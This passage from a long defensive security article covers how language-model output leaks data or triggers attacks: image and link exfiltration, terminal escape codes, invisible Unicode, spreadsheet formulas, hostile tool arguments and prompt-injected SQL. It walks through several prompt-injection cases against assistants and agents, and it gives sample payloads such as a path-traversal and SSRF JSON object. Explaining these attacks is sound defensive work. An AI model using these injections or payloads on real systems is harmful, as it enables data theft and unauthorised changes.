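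The signatures in CamoLeak worked correctly. The data leaked through which images the assistant displayed, which the attacker could observe because the proxy fetched each image at the time of display. A proxy could instead fetch every image in an email or code change on arrival, before any model reads it, and keep the copies. The attacker would then receive the same requests whatever the assistant later displayed. This works only if the proxy never fetches an image again, even after its copy expires, because a later fetch would reveal that the image was displayed.

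### Showing the address before a click

For links, an application can display the full address and ask the user to confirm. This offers some protection against crude attacks, since an employee who sees `?balance=40000` at the end of a supplier's address may well stop. Few people would notice the same number if it were scrambled, and long strings of letters and digits are common in harmless links.

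This defence works poorly against SearchLeak because the link that the victim clicked led to a real Microsoft website. The domain would have looked right, and only a careful reader would have found the instructions in the long query. The text around a link can also mislead the user, as the fake security notice did in ChatGPhish, Permiso's attack of May 2026. The user may then type a password into the attacker's page, in which case the address needn't carry any data. Even if the application shows the link's real domain, the user has to know which domain to expect.

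An assistant that asks users to confirm every link trains them to agree without reading. Users are more likely to read the request if the assistant asks only about addresses it has some reason to distrust, but it then needs a way to recognise the safe ones.

### Fetching only known addresses

An assistant that reads web pages constantly sends requests, and a company can't list every useful website in advance. It can instead restrict where the addresses come from. In *The Memory Heist*, a July report on Anthropic's Claude, Paul (2026) found that Claude's web tool would open an address only if the user had typed it, it appeared in search results, or a page Claude had already fetched linked to it. When Paul asked Claude to add a name to the end of a web address and visit it, the tool would not open the resulting address.

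The third case left an opening because attackers control the links on their own pages. Paul built a website whose first page linked to 27 others, one for each letter of the alphabet and one for the hyphen. Each of those linked to 27 more, and so on. Claude could spell out a word by following one link per character, and the tool allowed every address it opened. Paul's server recorded the visits as Claude spelled out "ayush-paul".

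Paul still had to get Claude to do this. Claude tended not to follow simple injected instructions, so Paul disguised the site as a coffee shop behind a security check, which claimed that AI assistants had to identify themselves by their user's name. Claude keeps a summary of past conversations and can search them, so it had access to a lot of information about the user. Paul reports that it disclosed a full name, an employer and the answers to security questions, and that nothing in the conversation showed this. The test used Paul's own account, so it demonstrated the flaw without taking anyone else's data.

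A stricter rule allows the assistant to open only addresses that are already known to be public. OpenAI described such a check for ChatGPT in early 2026. The check uses an index of web addresses that a crawler has found without access to anyone's conversations. ChatGPT can open an address automatically if it is in the index. Otherwise, it looks for another source or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

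The reasoning behind this check is sound because a crawler that has never seen an employee's mailbox is very unlikely to have recorded an address containing the employee's bank balance. The check also defeats Paul's website as it stood, which created its pages on demand. Covering every ten-character name would take 27¹⁰, or about 206 trillion, pages, far more than any crawler would index.

An attacker could get by with far fewer pages, though. For ten characters, 270 ordinary pages would be enough, one for each possible character in each position. The attacker could publish them, wait for the crawler to find them and then have the assistant visit one page per position. The check stops the assistant from composing an address, but the assistant could still choose among these 270 public ones, and each choice would reveal one character to the attacker.

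### How much a choice reveals

A bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. If an assistant can request any of *N* permitted addresses, and the attacker can see which one it requested, a single request conveys up to log₂ *N* bits. With 64 addresses, this is 6 bits, because 2⁶ = 64. There are *N*ᵏ possible sequences of *k* requests, so a sequence conveys up to *k* × log₂ *N* bits.

Paul's pages each had 27 links, so each request could carry about 4.75 bits. CamoLeak worked the same way with images. An address that the model can write freely can carry far more. If each of 2,000 characters can be any of 64 symbols, one request carries 12,000 bits.

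The table shows how many requests an attacker would need for three kinds of secret. A six-digit login code has a million possible values, or about 20 bits. A sixteen-digit number has about 53 bits, and encryption keys often have 256.

| Permitted addresses | Bits per request | Six-digit code | Sixteen-digit number | 256-bit key |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 20 | 54 | 256 |
| 27 | 4.75 | 5 | 12 | 54 |
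| 64 | 6 | 4 | 9 | 43 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.9 | 1 | 3 | 13 |

Shortening the list of addresses helps less than one might expect, because the number of bits each request can carry grows only with the logarithm of the list's length. If the list is cut from a million addresses to 64, the attacker still needs only four requests instead of one to get the login code.

These figures are upper limits on what the choice of address can reveal. The attacker learns less if the assistant makes mistakes while spelling out the data or if its requests arrive out of order. The attacker may also learn something from the timing of requests or from their absence. Even if only one address is permitted, the attacker could send an email instructing the assistant to open that address only if the company is planning redundancies, then learn the answer from whether a request arrives.

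Limiting the number of requests reduces the data an attacker can extract in proportion. If each request can go to any of 64 addresses, it carries six bits, so ten requests carry about 60. A limit of ten protects documents well, since a 3,000-character page would take 3,000 requests at one character each, but it doesn't protect a six-digit login code, which takes four. A request limit alone can keep the code entirely safe only by allowing no requests that the attacker can observe, because even one request to one of 64 addresses narrows the possible codes from a million to about 16,000.

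The limit also has to cover a long enough period. Ten requests per reply add up to 200 over 20 replies, which can carry 1,200 bits, enough for several encryption keys. An attacker who can send more emails can ask for a different part of the secret each time. A daily limit for each user closes this gap but soon interferes with normal use, because an assistant doing legitimate research may open 50 pages in an afternoon. A limit per website is less disruptive, since few tasks need 50 pages from one unfamiliar site. The attacker can get around it by spreading the pages over several sites, though this takes extra effort.

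Counting is unnecessary if the attacker can't see the requests. An assistant could read stored copies of pages that a crawler had collected beforehand, as ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode does by limiting browsing to cached pages. Even if the assistant chose among a million addresses, their owners wouldn't see which one it picked. The copies may be out of date, which matters a lot for a share price but little for a supplier's terms of business.

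## Control characters in terminals, editors and spreadsheets

Text printed in a terminal can create a misleading link or, in at least one program, trigger a network request, even though terminals don't display web images or enforce a Content Security Policy (CSP). OWASP added terminals to its entry on output handling only in 2026, though the flaw is much older than language models.

### How a terminal finds commands in text

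Terminals use in-band signalling, which means that commands arrive in the same stream as the text they affect. Most commands begin with the escape character, number 27 in the ASCII character set, which has no visible shape. The usual commands are known as ANSI escape codes. For example, a program might print this, with ESC standing for that single character:

```
ESC[31mOverdueESC[0m
```

A terminal that receives `\x1b[31mOverdue\x1b[0m`, where `\x1b` is the escape character, shows the word "Overdue" in red. The `31` selects the colour, the `m` marks a command about the text's appearance, and the `0` restores the normal style. Other codes move the cursor, clear the screen, or create a link whose visible text differs from its address. In some terminals, a code can write to the clipboard.

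HTML encoding does nothing here because the example contains none of the characters it replaces. It also garbles harmless text. For example, a terminal would show the supplier name Smith & Sons as `Smith &amp; Sons`.

Most of these codes can only deceive the reader, but in some terminals they could do more. GCVE's *CWE-150* includes a 2003 flaw in the terminal xterm, where a hostile file could set the window's title and then have the terminal insert that title into the command line. In April 2026, users in Hacker News' *Even "cat readme.txt" is not safe* discussed a flaw in iTerm2, a Mac terminal, which accepted its remote login feature's private commands from any text a program printed. A developer rarely knows which terminal a customer uses, so a filter can't rely on a list of dangerous codes.

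### Codes that arrive through a model

*The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) describes an early case from 2023, in which the agent program AutoGPT printed the text of fetched web pages to the console with any escape codes intact. A hostile page could use these codes to hide commands the agent had run, or to trick the operator into approving one. A better model would not have prevented this, because the codes went straight from the page to the console.

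In November 2024, the researcher Leon Derczynski reported that many models can also write the escape character themselves. The following week, *Terminal DiLLMa*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red, demonstrated the consequences with a small program that sent a document to OpenAI's GPT-4o and printed the reply. When the program summarised a hostile web page, printing the reply changed the text's colour, moved the cursor, cleared the screen and sounded a beep.

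In further tests, control codes put text on the clipboard. Most terminals, but not all, removed the final line break, so a pasted command would not run until the user pressed Enter. In the terminal built into the code editor VS Code, a reply could contain a link with private text in its address, but the editor asked for confirmation before opening it. In Apple's Terminal, a control code could trigger a lookup of a domain name containing text from the prompt, which sent that text to whoever ran the domain's server without the user clicking anything.

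Models didn't always produce the codes on request. But Embrace The Red found that models could also read the codes, so an attacker could put them in a document and ask the model to repeat them. A model with a code execution tool could also run a program that printed the codes.

In April 2025, the security company Trail of Bits tested version 0.2.76 of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent for the terminal. *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* reports that Claude Code did not filter escape codes from the descriptions or output of outside tools connected through the Model Context Protocol (MCP). In one test, a tool's reply included an instruction in white letters to send Windows users to a particular server for Python packages. The user saw a gap in the text, while the model read the instruction and recommended the server.

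White text is invisible only on a white background, and many programmers use a dark one. Trail of Bits also described methods that work on any background. One moves the cursor back up and prints a reassuring security report over the malicious instructions. Another clears the screen and adds blank lines so that the window appears to have scrolled.

### Repairs in coding agents since then

Coding agents have added filters gradually. Hoxha changed the agent Crush to show control characters in tool output as visible text (*Merge pull request #176 from charmbracelet/escape-sequences*). A March 2026 fix to OpenClaw, another agent, stopped a tool's title from altering the appearance of the user's approval prompt. According to GCVE, the fix also widened an existing filter that had recognised only some escape codes.

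In July 2026, Anthropic stopped control characters in background agents' output from reaching the terminal in one of Claude Code's views. Anthropic (2026) lists more fixes in its October release notes. Claude Code's built-in GitHub command no longer sends control characters from file names and error messages to the terminal. Skills, which are reusable sets of instructions, can no longer run shell commands that contain raw control characters, and a message shows the user where the characters are.

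None of these repairs concerns the MCP tool descriptions that Trail of Bits tested, so we can't tell from them whether or when that route was closed. But they show how a product can filter text in one view and miss it in another. A safer design passes all text through one function just before display. *sanitize.rs*, part of a library for building terminal programs, does this by default and treats logs, tool output and model replies as data.

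### Removing the codes or making them visible

Trail of Bits recommends replacing every escape character with a placeholder, on the grounds that all the sequences modern terminals recognise begin with it. This stops most attacks but misses the C1 controls, single characters that can take the place of the escape character and the bracket after it. *atomcode-tuix 4.23.1*, the source code of another coding agent, removes these too. Backspaces also need removing, because they can erase text already on the screen.

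MITRE's *CWE-150* has a broader rule of allowing only printable characters and chosen kinds of white space. MITRE gives the carriage return as an example of permitted white space, but a carriage return on its own moves the cursor to the start of the line, where later text can overwrite what was there. An application can keep carriage returns that are part of a line break and remove the rest.

Filtering single characters also works when replies arrive in pieces. If an escape code is split between two pieces, the application still removes the escape character, and the remainder appears as harmless stray text such as `[31m`. A filter that searches for complete codes has to store the unfinished code until the rest arrives.

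Removing control characters tidies an ordinary reply but can be dangerous in an approval prompt. MITRE describes an application that removed escape codes from a file name when asking for permission but kept them in the name it then used, so the user could grant access to the wrong file. The application should either reject such a name or make the codes visible. Embrace The Red suggests caret notation, which writes the escape character as `^[`. The Unix command `cat -v` uses the same notation when it prints a file.

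If replies need colour, the application can permit only specific escape codes, such as those for red, green, bold and restoring the normal style, and should exclude the code that conceals text. It is better to filter the reply first and have the application add colours based on the Markdown, so the model never needs to output an escape character.

Ordinary characters can also hide a command. Tracebit's *Research takeaway* reports that in Google's Gemini CLI, a lot of white space seemed to help hide a malicious command from the user. No control character filter would catch this. Since late October, one of Claude Code's permission screens has blocked users from approving a call they can't read in full, even when the terminal window is just too short to show it all.

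### Logs

OWASP recommends logging model output, but a log can contain escape codes that a terminal executes when someone displays the file, perhaps months later. In *Weaponizing Plain Text*, STÖK (2023) demonstrated a fake error message whose link appeared to lead to Microsoft's help site but pointed to a program on the reader's own computer.

Control codes can also hide evidence. Inspektor Gadget, a tool that monitors running software, printed file names without filtering them. In a demonstration recorded by GCVE, a program read the system's protected password file and then created a file with cursor codes in its name. When the tool printed that name, the codes altered the earlier line so that it appeared to record access to a harmless file.

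The tool's JSON output was already safe from raw escape characters, because JSON, a common text format for data, requires programs to write the escape character as the visible sequence `\u001b`. JSON doesn't require this for C1 controls or invisible Unicode characters, which Claude Code began to escape in its JSON output in October. Anthropic notes that the values are unchanged after parsing. A log viewer that parses the JSON and prints a message therefore restores the original characters and needs its own filter.

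### What CWE-150 covers

CWE-150 applies when a product passes on input without properly neutralising characters that the next component could interpret as escape, meta or control sequences. MITRE added advice on language models to the entry on 30 April 2026. It rates filtering before display as highly effective. It also suggests removing escape codes from a model's token vocabulary, but rates the effectiveness of this as limited because the model might still assemble a code from several tokens.

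MITRE allows CWE-150 to be used for real vulnerabilities, unlike CWE-1426, the number for unchecked AI output. GCVE lists 156 records under CWE-150, many of them unrelated to models and some unrelated to terminals. MITRE's *CVE-2026-19591* classifies a flaw in OpenAI's coding agent Codex under CWE-150. According to the Zero Day Initiative's advisory (2026), the flaw was in the arguments of commands for git, the version control program. Until OpenAI fixed it, an attacker could run code on the computer of anyone who opened a malicious folder.

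### Invisible and direction-changing characters in editors

Unicode, the standard that numbers the characters of the world's writing systems, includes invisible characters that affect how software joins or orders the characters around them. An editor applies these effects when it displays text, but a compiler or shell processes the characters as stored, so a reviewer can approve something different from what runs.

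The right-to-left override makes an editor display the characters after it in reverse. Suppose the office assistant saves a file whose name consists of `invoice-`, this character and `fdp.exe`. The employee sees `invoice-exe.pdf`, which looks like a document but is a program. In source code, the same trick can make an instruction look like part of a comment.

Other characters can hide whole messages. *On Seeding Watermarks to Detect Verbatim LLM Copy-Paste Responses* (2026) describes the Tags block, a range of characters that duplicates printable ASCII but is displayed by almost no font. *Reverse CAPTCHA* (2026) compares the Tags block with a method that encodes text in binary, using two zero-width characters as 0 and 1. The 12 characters of "Reply VIOLET" become 12 tag characters or 96 zero-width characters.

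Variation selectors, which choose between two styles of a symbol, are more compact. There are 256, so each can carry 8 bits, and three are enough for a six-digit login code. According to *Imperceptible Jailbreaking against Large Language Models* (2025), the selectors survive copying and pasting. A hostile email could cause the office assistant to hide the code in a draft, which the employee then pastes into a message to the supplier. Blocking images and links wouldn't prevent this, because the employee sends the data.

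An application can't simply delete all these characters, because many languages and emoji need them.

| Character | Effect in an editor | Ordinary text that needs it |
|---|---|---|
| Right-to-left override | Reverses the characters after it | Almost none, since Hebrew and Arabic letters have their own direction |
| Direction marks and isolates | Keep mixed text in the right order | Hebrew or Arabic sentences with English names |
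| Zero-width joiner and non-joiner | Join or separate neighbouring characters | Persian and Hindi words, family emoji |
| Variation selectors | Choose a symbol's style | Coloured emoji, such as some check marks |
| Tags | Usually none | Flag emoji for England, Scotland and Wales |

How an application should treat these characters depends on the kind of text. In commands, file names and source code, it can reject them or display their code points, such as `U+202E`. A programmer who needs one inside a Persian phrase can write it as a visible escape sequence. In prose, the application can remove overrides and keep the other characters only where they have a normal function. For example, it can keep a single variation selector after a symbol that has two styles.

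Since October, Claude Code has ignored skills whose names contain hidden or direction-changing characters until someone renames them. But some Persian and Hindi words and some emoji legitimately contain zero-width characters. Releasebot's *Claude Code Updates & Release Notes* (2026) lists a December fix for a bug that stopped users from reopening a saved session by name if the name contained these characters.

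Finding invisible characters requires testing in more than one program. *Data Provenance Auditing of Fine-Tuned Large Language Models with a Text-Preserving Technique* (2025) tested 235 control and format characters in a terminal, a text document and a table file. It found 130 that were invisible in all three, but warns that some of these may be visible in other editors or browsers.

Visible characters can also mislead. ThaiCERT's *Critical Vulnerability in OpenAI Codex Could Allow GitHub Token Theft* (2026) describes commands hidden in the names of git branches, which are separate lines of work on a program. The attack used ideographic spaces, which are meant for Chinese and Japanese text but look like ordinary spaces. A filter for invisible format characters would not remove them. An application that expects a branch name should check that the name contains only permitted characters, and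 pass it to other programs as a value, separate from the command.

### Spreadsheet cells that begin a formula

The office assistant may also export a table as a CSV file, which is plain text with commas between the cells. The file doesn't mark cells as text or formulas, so the spreadsheet program uses each cell's first character to distinguish them. An equals sign starts a formula, and in many programs a plus sign, a minus sign or an `@` can too.

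A spreadsheet formula can read other cells and put their contents into a link's address. In some programs it can also request a web address by itself, and in older versions of Excel it could start other programs. Spreadsheet programs often warn the user first, but an employee opening a file from the company's own assistant has little reason to heed the warning. A supplier could put a formula in its company name, and the model would insert it into the spreadsheet just by copying the name accurately.

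Quotation marks around a cell don't stop a spreadsheet program from treating its contents as a formula, because the program removes them before it checks the first character. They are still necessary, because without them the name `Smith,=1+1` would become two cells. The second would be a formula, which a check on the first character of the name would miss.

The common fix is to put an apostrophe before any cell that starts with one of these characters, so that the spreadsheet treats it as text. This also turns negative numbers into text. Suppose a company has invoices from a supplier for €1,200 and €300 and a credit note for −€450, so it owes €1,050. If the credit note becomes text, the spreadsheet's sum function ignores it and shows €1,500. Telephone numbers that begin with a plus sign may also gain a visible apostrophe.

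The application should therefore handle each value according to its column's type. In a column of amounts, it can accept `-450` as a number and reject anything that isn't one. It needs the apostrophe only in text columns. If the employee wants totals, the application can write those formulas itself.

Excel's own file format is a better fix because it stores each cell's type separately from its value. The application can mark a company name as text, much as a parameterised query keeps a value separate from the command. Some programming libraries turn any text that starts with an equals sign into a formula by default, so a developer should export `=1+1` as a name and check that the cell doesn't show 2. The protection is lost if the employee saves the table as CSV and opens it again, because CSV doesn't store the type and the program calculates the formula.

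## Checking structured output and database queries

Applications can request an object with separate, typed fields from a language model instead of prose. These fields are easier to check, but each can still hold a dangerous value. A database query is harder to check than these fields because the model may write all of it.

### Asking for a fixed form

Most applications ask for structured output in JSON, in which every value has a name. A JSON schema lists the names and the type of each value. The schema for an expense claim might require an `amount` that is a number and a `currency` that is one of two codes. The arguments in a tool call usually have a schema too.

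If the schema is only included in the prompt, the model may leave out a field or put a sentence before the object. The application therefore has to parse the reply and reject it if it doesn't match the schema. JSON schemas allow fields they don't define unless the developer adds `"additionalProperties": false`. If the application passes the whole object on, the next program may act on a field the developer didn't anticipate.

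Constrained decoding prevents formatting errors while the model is writing. At each step, the model gives every next token *i* a score *z*ᵢ, and the token's probability is exp(*z*ᵢ) divided by the sum of exp(*z*ⱼ) over all tokens *j*. A separate program tracks the output's position in the grammar and sets the score of every token that would violate the grammar to −∞. Since exp(−∞) is 0, the model can't produce those tokens.

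Suppose an invoice is in Swiss francs, but the schema allows only euros and dollars. For simplicity, assume each currency code is one token, with scores of 3 for CHF, 2 for EUR and 1 for USD. Without the constraint, the model writes CHF 67% of the time and EUR 24%. With it, CHF drops to 0% and EUR rises to 73%. The output now always fits the schema, but it always names the wrong currency. Adding "other" to the permitted values would fix this.

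The application should still validate the finished object, because a reply that reaches its length limit can stop in the middle of a field.

### A valid object with hostile values

Suppose the office assistant has a tool that downloads an invoice from a supplier's website and saves it in the folder `/shared/invoices/`. The tool takes two strings, and a supplier's email leads the model to write this:

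```
{
  "file_name": "../payroll/march.csv",
  "source": "http://127.0.0.1/admin/users"
}
```

The object is valid JSON and fits the schema. Constrained decoding wouldn't have prevented it either, because a JSON string can contain almost any character.

In a file path, two dots mean the folder above, so when the application joins the folder and the file name, the resulting path leads to `/shared/payroll/march.csv`. This is path traversal, in which a file name leads outside the intended folder. The second value would cause server-side request forgery. The address `127.0.0.1` always refers to the computer that sends the request, here the company's own server, which may show its administration page only to requests from itself. The tool would download a list of users and overwrite the March payroll with it.

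Deleting `../` from the file name is a poor fix, because removing it from `....//` leaves `../`. The application should work out the full path, following any symbolic links, and then check that the result starts with `/shared/invoices/`. Without the final slash, the check would also accept `/shared/invoices-old/`. Better still, the application can name the file itself, using the invoice number.

Blocking the text `127.0.0.1` fails for a similar reason, because many programs accept the number 2130706433 as the same address. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, recommend converting the address to a standard form before checking it, and rejecting unsafe schemes, hosts, redirects and private network ranges. The application also has to connect to the same numerical address it checked, because the owner of a domain name can point the name to a different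 address after the check. Firewall rules that block the tool from internal services would catch whatever these checks miss.

Every argument needs a check that depends on what the tool does with it.

| Argument | Well-formed but harmful value | Check or repair |
|---|---|---|
| File name | A path into another folder | Work out the full path and require it to be inside the permitted folder |
| Web address | A page on the internal network | Check the scheme, host and numerical address, again after each redirect |
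| Record number | Another customer's order | Search only the records this user may see |
| Payment amount | A hundred times the invoice | Compare it with the unpaid balance |
| Part of a shell command | A value with a second command added | Pass it as a separate value, without a shell |
| XML document | A reference to a private file | Turn off external references in the XML parser |
| Setting that skips a confirmation | "Yes" | Remove it from the tool's arguments and set it in code |

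Record numbers are easy to overlook because they look harmless. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a public chatbot that looked up orders by a number consisting of `ABC` and six digits. A schema can enforce that pattern, but the chatbot also needed to check that the order belonged to the person asking. It never did, so it gave out other customers' email addresses and delivery details.

### When the allow-list is only in the prompt

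Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian also built a concert website with an assistant whose only tool fetched any web address the model supplied. An administration service on the same server accepted requests only from that server. In April 2026, they tried four kinds of direct attack on seven models, ten times each. Llama 3.3 made the forbidden request in all 40 attempts, while GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 never did. Gemini 3 Pro Preview refused to probe the server for open ports, but in all ten attempts it fetched an address that deleted records.

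They then put a list of permitted addresses in the prompt and told the models to refuse all others. This stopped every direct attack. But when they planted a concert review with a false notice that the list had been extended, Llama 3.3 fetched the forbidden page in all ten attempts. Without the list, a planted review had worked six times. The two reviews had different wording, so the increase doesn't prove that the list made Llama more vulnerable, but the list didn't protect it from the planted review.

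The better fix is for the tool to accept only an event name from the model. The application then checks the name and builds the address itself, so no review can make the tool contact the administration service.

### Where parameterised queries stop helping

When the employee asks how much the company still owes its paper supplier, the application can use a parameterised query:

```
SELECT SUM(amount) FROM invoices WHERE supplier = ? AND paid = 0
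```

The model provides only the supplier's name, and the placeholder keeps that name from changing the query's structure. But the placeholder doesn't check that the name is appropriate, so the query also runs with a different supplier's name. If the query used `LIKE`, which allows partial matches, a single `%` would match every supplier.

A placeholder also can't stand for a table, a column or an operation, so it gives no protection when the model writes the whole query. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian therefore call prepared statements (parameterised queries) necessary for values but insufficient in this case. *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* (2026), a survey of systems that turn questions into SQL, recommends read-only execution and output validation as well.

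### One question, five safeguards

Suppose the model itself writes the query for the paper supplier. Normally, it produces the query above with the name filled in. After reading a hostile email, it might instead write a query that deletes the invoices or looks up salaries. The company can limit the damage in five ways.

With fixed templates, the developer writes a few dozen queries in advance, and the model chooses one and fills in the values. The model can't delete anything because no template does, but it also can't answer a question that nobody foresaw, such as which suppliers have raised their prices since spring. *Please Don't Kill My Vibe* (2025) criticises designs like this for requiring developers to predict every future need for data. That limitation matters little for an assistant that mostly looks up balances, but it would defeat the purpose of a tool for analysts.

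The application can parse the model's SQL into a tree and accept only a single `SELECT` on permitted tables and columns. *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control* (Fei and Yang, 2026) expresses such a rule with sets. Perm(*q*) is the set of all combinations of table, column and operation that query *q* uses, and Π is the set of combinations that the user's role permits. The query may run only if Perm(*q*) ⊆ Π. The query for the paper supplier reads the `amount`, `supplier` and `paid` columns of the invoice table, so it passes for a clerk who may read all three. If the model adds a subquery on salaries, Perm(*q*) includes a combination outside Π and the application rejects the query.

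Searching the query text for forbidden words is much weaker than parsing it. A word search would block a question about a supplier called Drop Logistics but allow a query that reads salaries. The parser has to use the same SQL dialect as the database. The application also needs a list of permitted functions, because in some databases a `SELECT` can call functions that read files on the server.

The assistant can connect to the database through an account whose only permission is to read the invoice tables. The database then rejects deletions even if a parser fault lets them through.

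**Row-level permissions.** If each clerk handles the suppliers in one region, the database can add that restriction to every query, so a request for all invoices returns only those from the clerk's suppliers. This works only if the database can identify the clerk. Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026) warn in *Data Agents Under Attack* that many assistants use one shared account, which hides the user's identity from the database. The application should take the clerk's identity from the login session, never from the model's output, and block functions that let a query change the identity setting.

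**Limits on time and rows.** A harmless-looking query can occupy a database for hours. In one test by Wang and colleagues, an agent called LAMBDA combined two tables of 13.8 million rows each without a condition for matching rows, producing about 190 trillion pairs. At a billion pairs per second, this would take 53 hours. LAMBDA couldn't cancel the query and was unresponsive for 30 minutes. The database needs a time limit that stops the query itself. A limit on returned rows wouldn't have been enough, because a query that adds up 190 trillion pairs may return a single number, but it still helps prevent someone from copying a whole table.

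The table shows what each safeguard does about four bad queries.

| Safeguard | Deletes invoices | Reads salaries | Reads another region's invoices | Runs for hours |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed templates | Stops it | Stops it | Only if the template filters by user | Usually stops it |
| Parser with allow-list | Stops it | Stops it | No effect | Stops some cases |
| Read-only account for invoice tables | Stops it | Stops it | No effect | No effect |
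| Row-level permissions on invoices | Limits it to the clerk's region | No effect | Stops it | No effect |
| Time limit | No effect | No effect | No effect | Stops it |

None of these measures catches a permitted query that answers the wrong question. If the model's query doesn't subtract credit notes, the result overstates what the company owes. *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* recommends letting users in critical fields such as finance review and override the SQL. Few accounts clerks can read SQL, so the application could use the parsed query to display a plain description, such as "unpaid invoices only, credit notes left out".

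### Enforcing permissions while the model writes

Strict permissions make an assistant safe but can leave the employee without an answer. Fei and Yang point out that an otherwise correct query can fail because it uses one forbidden column. They added user roles to three existing benchmarks, producing 21,502 test cases, and found that putting the access rules in the prompt did not reliably prevent violations. Some models applied the rules correctly in their reasoning and then wrote a query that broke them. Fei and Yang want the database to keep enforcing the rules, and see giving the model the rules as a way to get more usable queries.

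*Policy-Conditioned Constrained Decoding for Column-Level Access Control in Text-to-SQL* (Miyamoto, Xin and Yamana, 2026) extends constrained decoding from enforcing grammar to enforcing permissions. Its system, PCC-SQL, tracks which part of the query the model is writing and blocks the names of columns that aren't allowed there. For example, a company could allow salaries only inside an average. A request for everyone's salary might then produce the average instead of a refusal.

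On a benchmark of 1,034 questions, Claude Opus 4.5 broke the rules in 20.4% of its answers, even though they were in its prompt. PCC-SQL with Qwen 2.5 Coder 7B, a far smaller model, never broke them. A checker that rejected every forbidden query would also prevent every violation, so PCC-SQL's advantage is that the employee more often gets a query that runs. The employee got one for 88.7% of questions with PCC-SQL and 58.2% with Claude Opus 4.5, or 68.4% when Claude could retry up to three times.

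A query that runs can still return the wrong result. With a larger Qwen model, PCC-SQL returned the correct result for only 48.2% of the questions whose ordinary answer the rules allowed. The guarantee covers only fairly simple SQL. The method also needs the model's token scores, so Miyamoto and colleagues could use it only with open models.

Averages and totals can also reveal individual values. In an example from Wang and colleagues, an agent gives the total tax for all regions and then for all regions except North, where only one taxpayer lives. The difference is that person's tax. Requiring a minimum group size wouldn't stop this, since both totals cover many people. The application has to track what a user has learned or add noise to the answers.

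### The first prompt-to-SQL study

*From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks* (Pedro, Carreira and colleagues, 2023) was the first study of prompt injections that make a model write harmful SQL. The researchers built a job-advert website with a chatbot that used GPT-3.5 and LangChain, a popular framework for language model applications. The chatbot's database account could read and change everything, so the model was the only safeguard against harmful queries. They ran each of seven attacks 30 times.

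With LangChain's standard prompt, the chatbot deleted a table when asked. The researchers then told the model to write only `SELECT` queries. It refused a direct request to ignore this rule, but complied every time the request included a made-up record showing that the same command had already succeeded. A rule against showing other people's data failed when the user claimed to be someone else.

Two attacks were indirect and used job adverts. One advert contained a false answer that made the chatbot tell other users there were no jobs. This attack always worked on a version that could send one query per question, and it worked 60% of the time on an agent that could send several. The other advert made the agent change a user's email address and then answer the original question as if nothing had happened. The changed address would let the attacker take over the account.

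The researchers repeated the restricted-prompt attacks on six more models, including GPT-4, PaLM 2 and Llama 2. GPT-4 resisted the email attack but none of the other attacks. PaLM 2 and Llama 2 changed the address but then mentioned it in the answer or got stuck in a loop. Two smaller models, Guanaco and Tulu, were too unreliable to run the agent.

For the defences, Pedro and colleagues added a chatbot to an online bookshop with about two million reviews.

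| Defence | Attacks it stopped | Added time |
|---|---|---|
| Read-only database account | Deletions and changes, including the email attack | Negligible |
| Rewriting each query to cover only the user's own rows | Reading other people's data | 1.87 milliseconds |
| Putting the user's data in the prompt beforehand | Reading other people's data | 0.7 milliseconds |
| A second model that inspects query results | Both indirect attacks | About 0.4 seconds |

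Together, the four defences stopped all seven attacks, but this was a modest test because the researchers had designed the defences with those attacks in mind. The first two don't depend on a model's judgement, so rewording an attack shouldn't defeat them. The second model is also vulnerable to injection, as Pedro and colleagues acknowledge. PostgreSQL, the database they used, supports permissions for columns and rows as well as whole tables, although they wrote that database permissions apply only to whole tables.

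### Tests on newer models

In their 2026 study, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian couldn't reproduce the 2023 techniques on the newer models. They didn't try to improve the prompts, though, so the result shows only that crude commands no longer work on those models.

Wang and colleagues planted subtler SQL in table cells and column comments, using real names from each database, where an agent would read it during ordinary analysis. On an open-source agent called DB-GPT, the attack succeeded in 12 of 25 tests with GPT-5.2, 11 with Claude Sonnet 4.6, and six each with Gemini 3 Flash and DeepSeek-V3.2. There were too few tests to rank the models. Any unauthorised effect counted as success, even one limited to a single reply, so these figures don't show how often tables were deleted.

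The attack worked in six of 25 tests on Google's BigQuery agent and in none on Databricks' agent. The Databricks agent often cited a policy when it refused, and Wang and colleagues credit its persistent instructions. Its access to data was also restricted, which may have helped.

OpenAI and Anthropic have since released models that do better on general injection tests, so the rates are probably lower now. A read-only account prevents deletions regardless of the rate.

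### Model output that LangChain loaded as trusted objects

LangChain had a serious flaw in how it serialised objects, which means turning them into text that can be stored and loaded again later. LangChain marks its own serialised objects with the key `lc`. Until December 2025, its functions `dumps()` and `dumpd()` did not escape ordinary data that contained the same key, so LangChain treated that data as one of its own objects when it loaded the text again.

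OSV's *PYSEC-2026-373* (2026), an entry in a database of open-source software flaws, is the advisory for this flaw, CVE-2025-68664. It identifies the most common route as `additional_kwargs` and `response_metadata`, two fields of a model's reply that can hold extra data of almost any shape. An attacker could influence these fields by prompt injection, and LangChain serialised and reloaded them during some streaming operations. An application could therefore be vulnerable to second-order injection, with the loading function as the sink, even if it loaded only data it had saved itself.

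Once LangChain accepted the data as an object, it could by default replace the data with a secret from the server's environment variables, where many applications keep passwords and access keys. It could also create objects from a list of approved classes. Cyata (2025), the security company that found the flaw, identified an approved class that contacts a server as soon as a program creates an instance of it, so an attacker could receive a secret without seeing any reply. Cyata found no way to run code through loading alone, but code could run if the application later used a loaded template.

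Cyata reported the flaw on 4 December 2025, and LangChain published a fix less than three weeks later. The US National Vulnerability Database record, *CVE-2025-68664* (2025), lists the fixed versions as 0.3.81 and 1.2.5. In these versions, `dumps()` and `dumpd()` wrap ordinary data containing the key, so that it is still ordinary data after loading. LangChain also changed its defaults to limit the damage from similar mistakes. It now creates fewer kinds of object, blocks a type of template that can run code, and takes secrets from the environment only if the developer allows it.

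The JavaScript version of LangChain had a similar flaw, described in OSV's *CVE-2025-68665* (2025). According to Cyata, the Python flaw went unnoticed for two and a half years, partly because a missing step is harder to spot than a wrong one, especially when it is missing from the code that saves data and the reviewer is studying the code that loads it. A short test would have found the flaw by saving a plain object that contains the reserved key, loading it again, and checking that it is still a plain object.

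## Running code that a model has written

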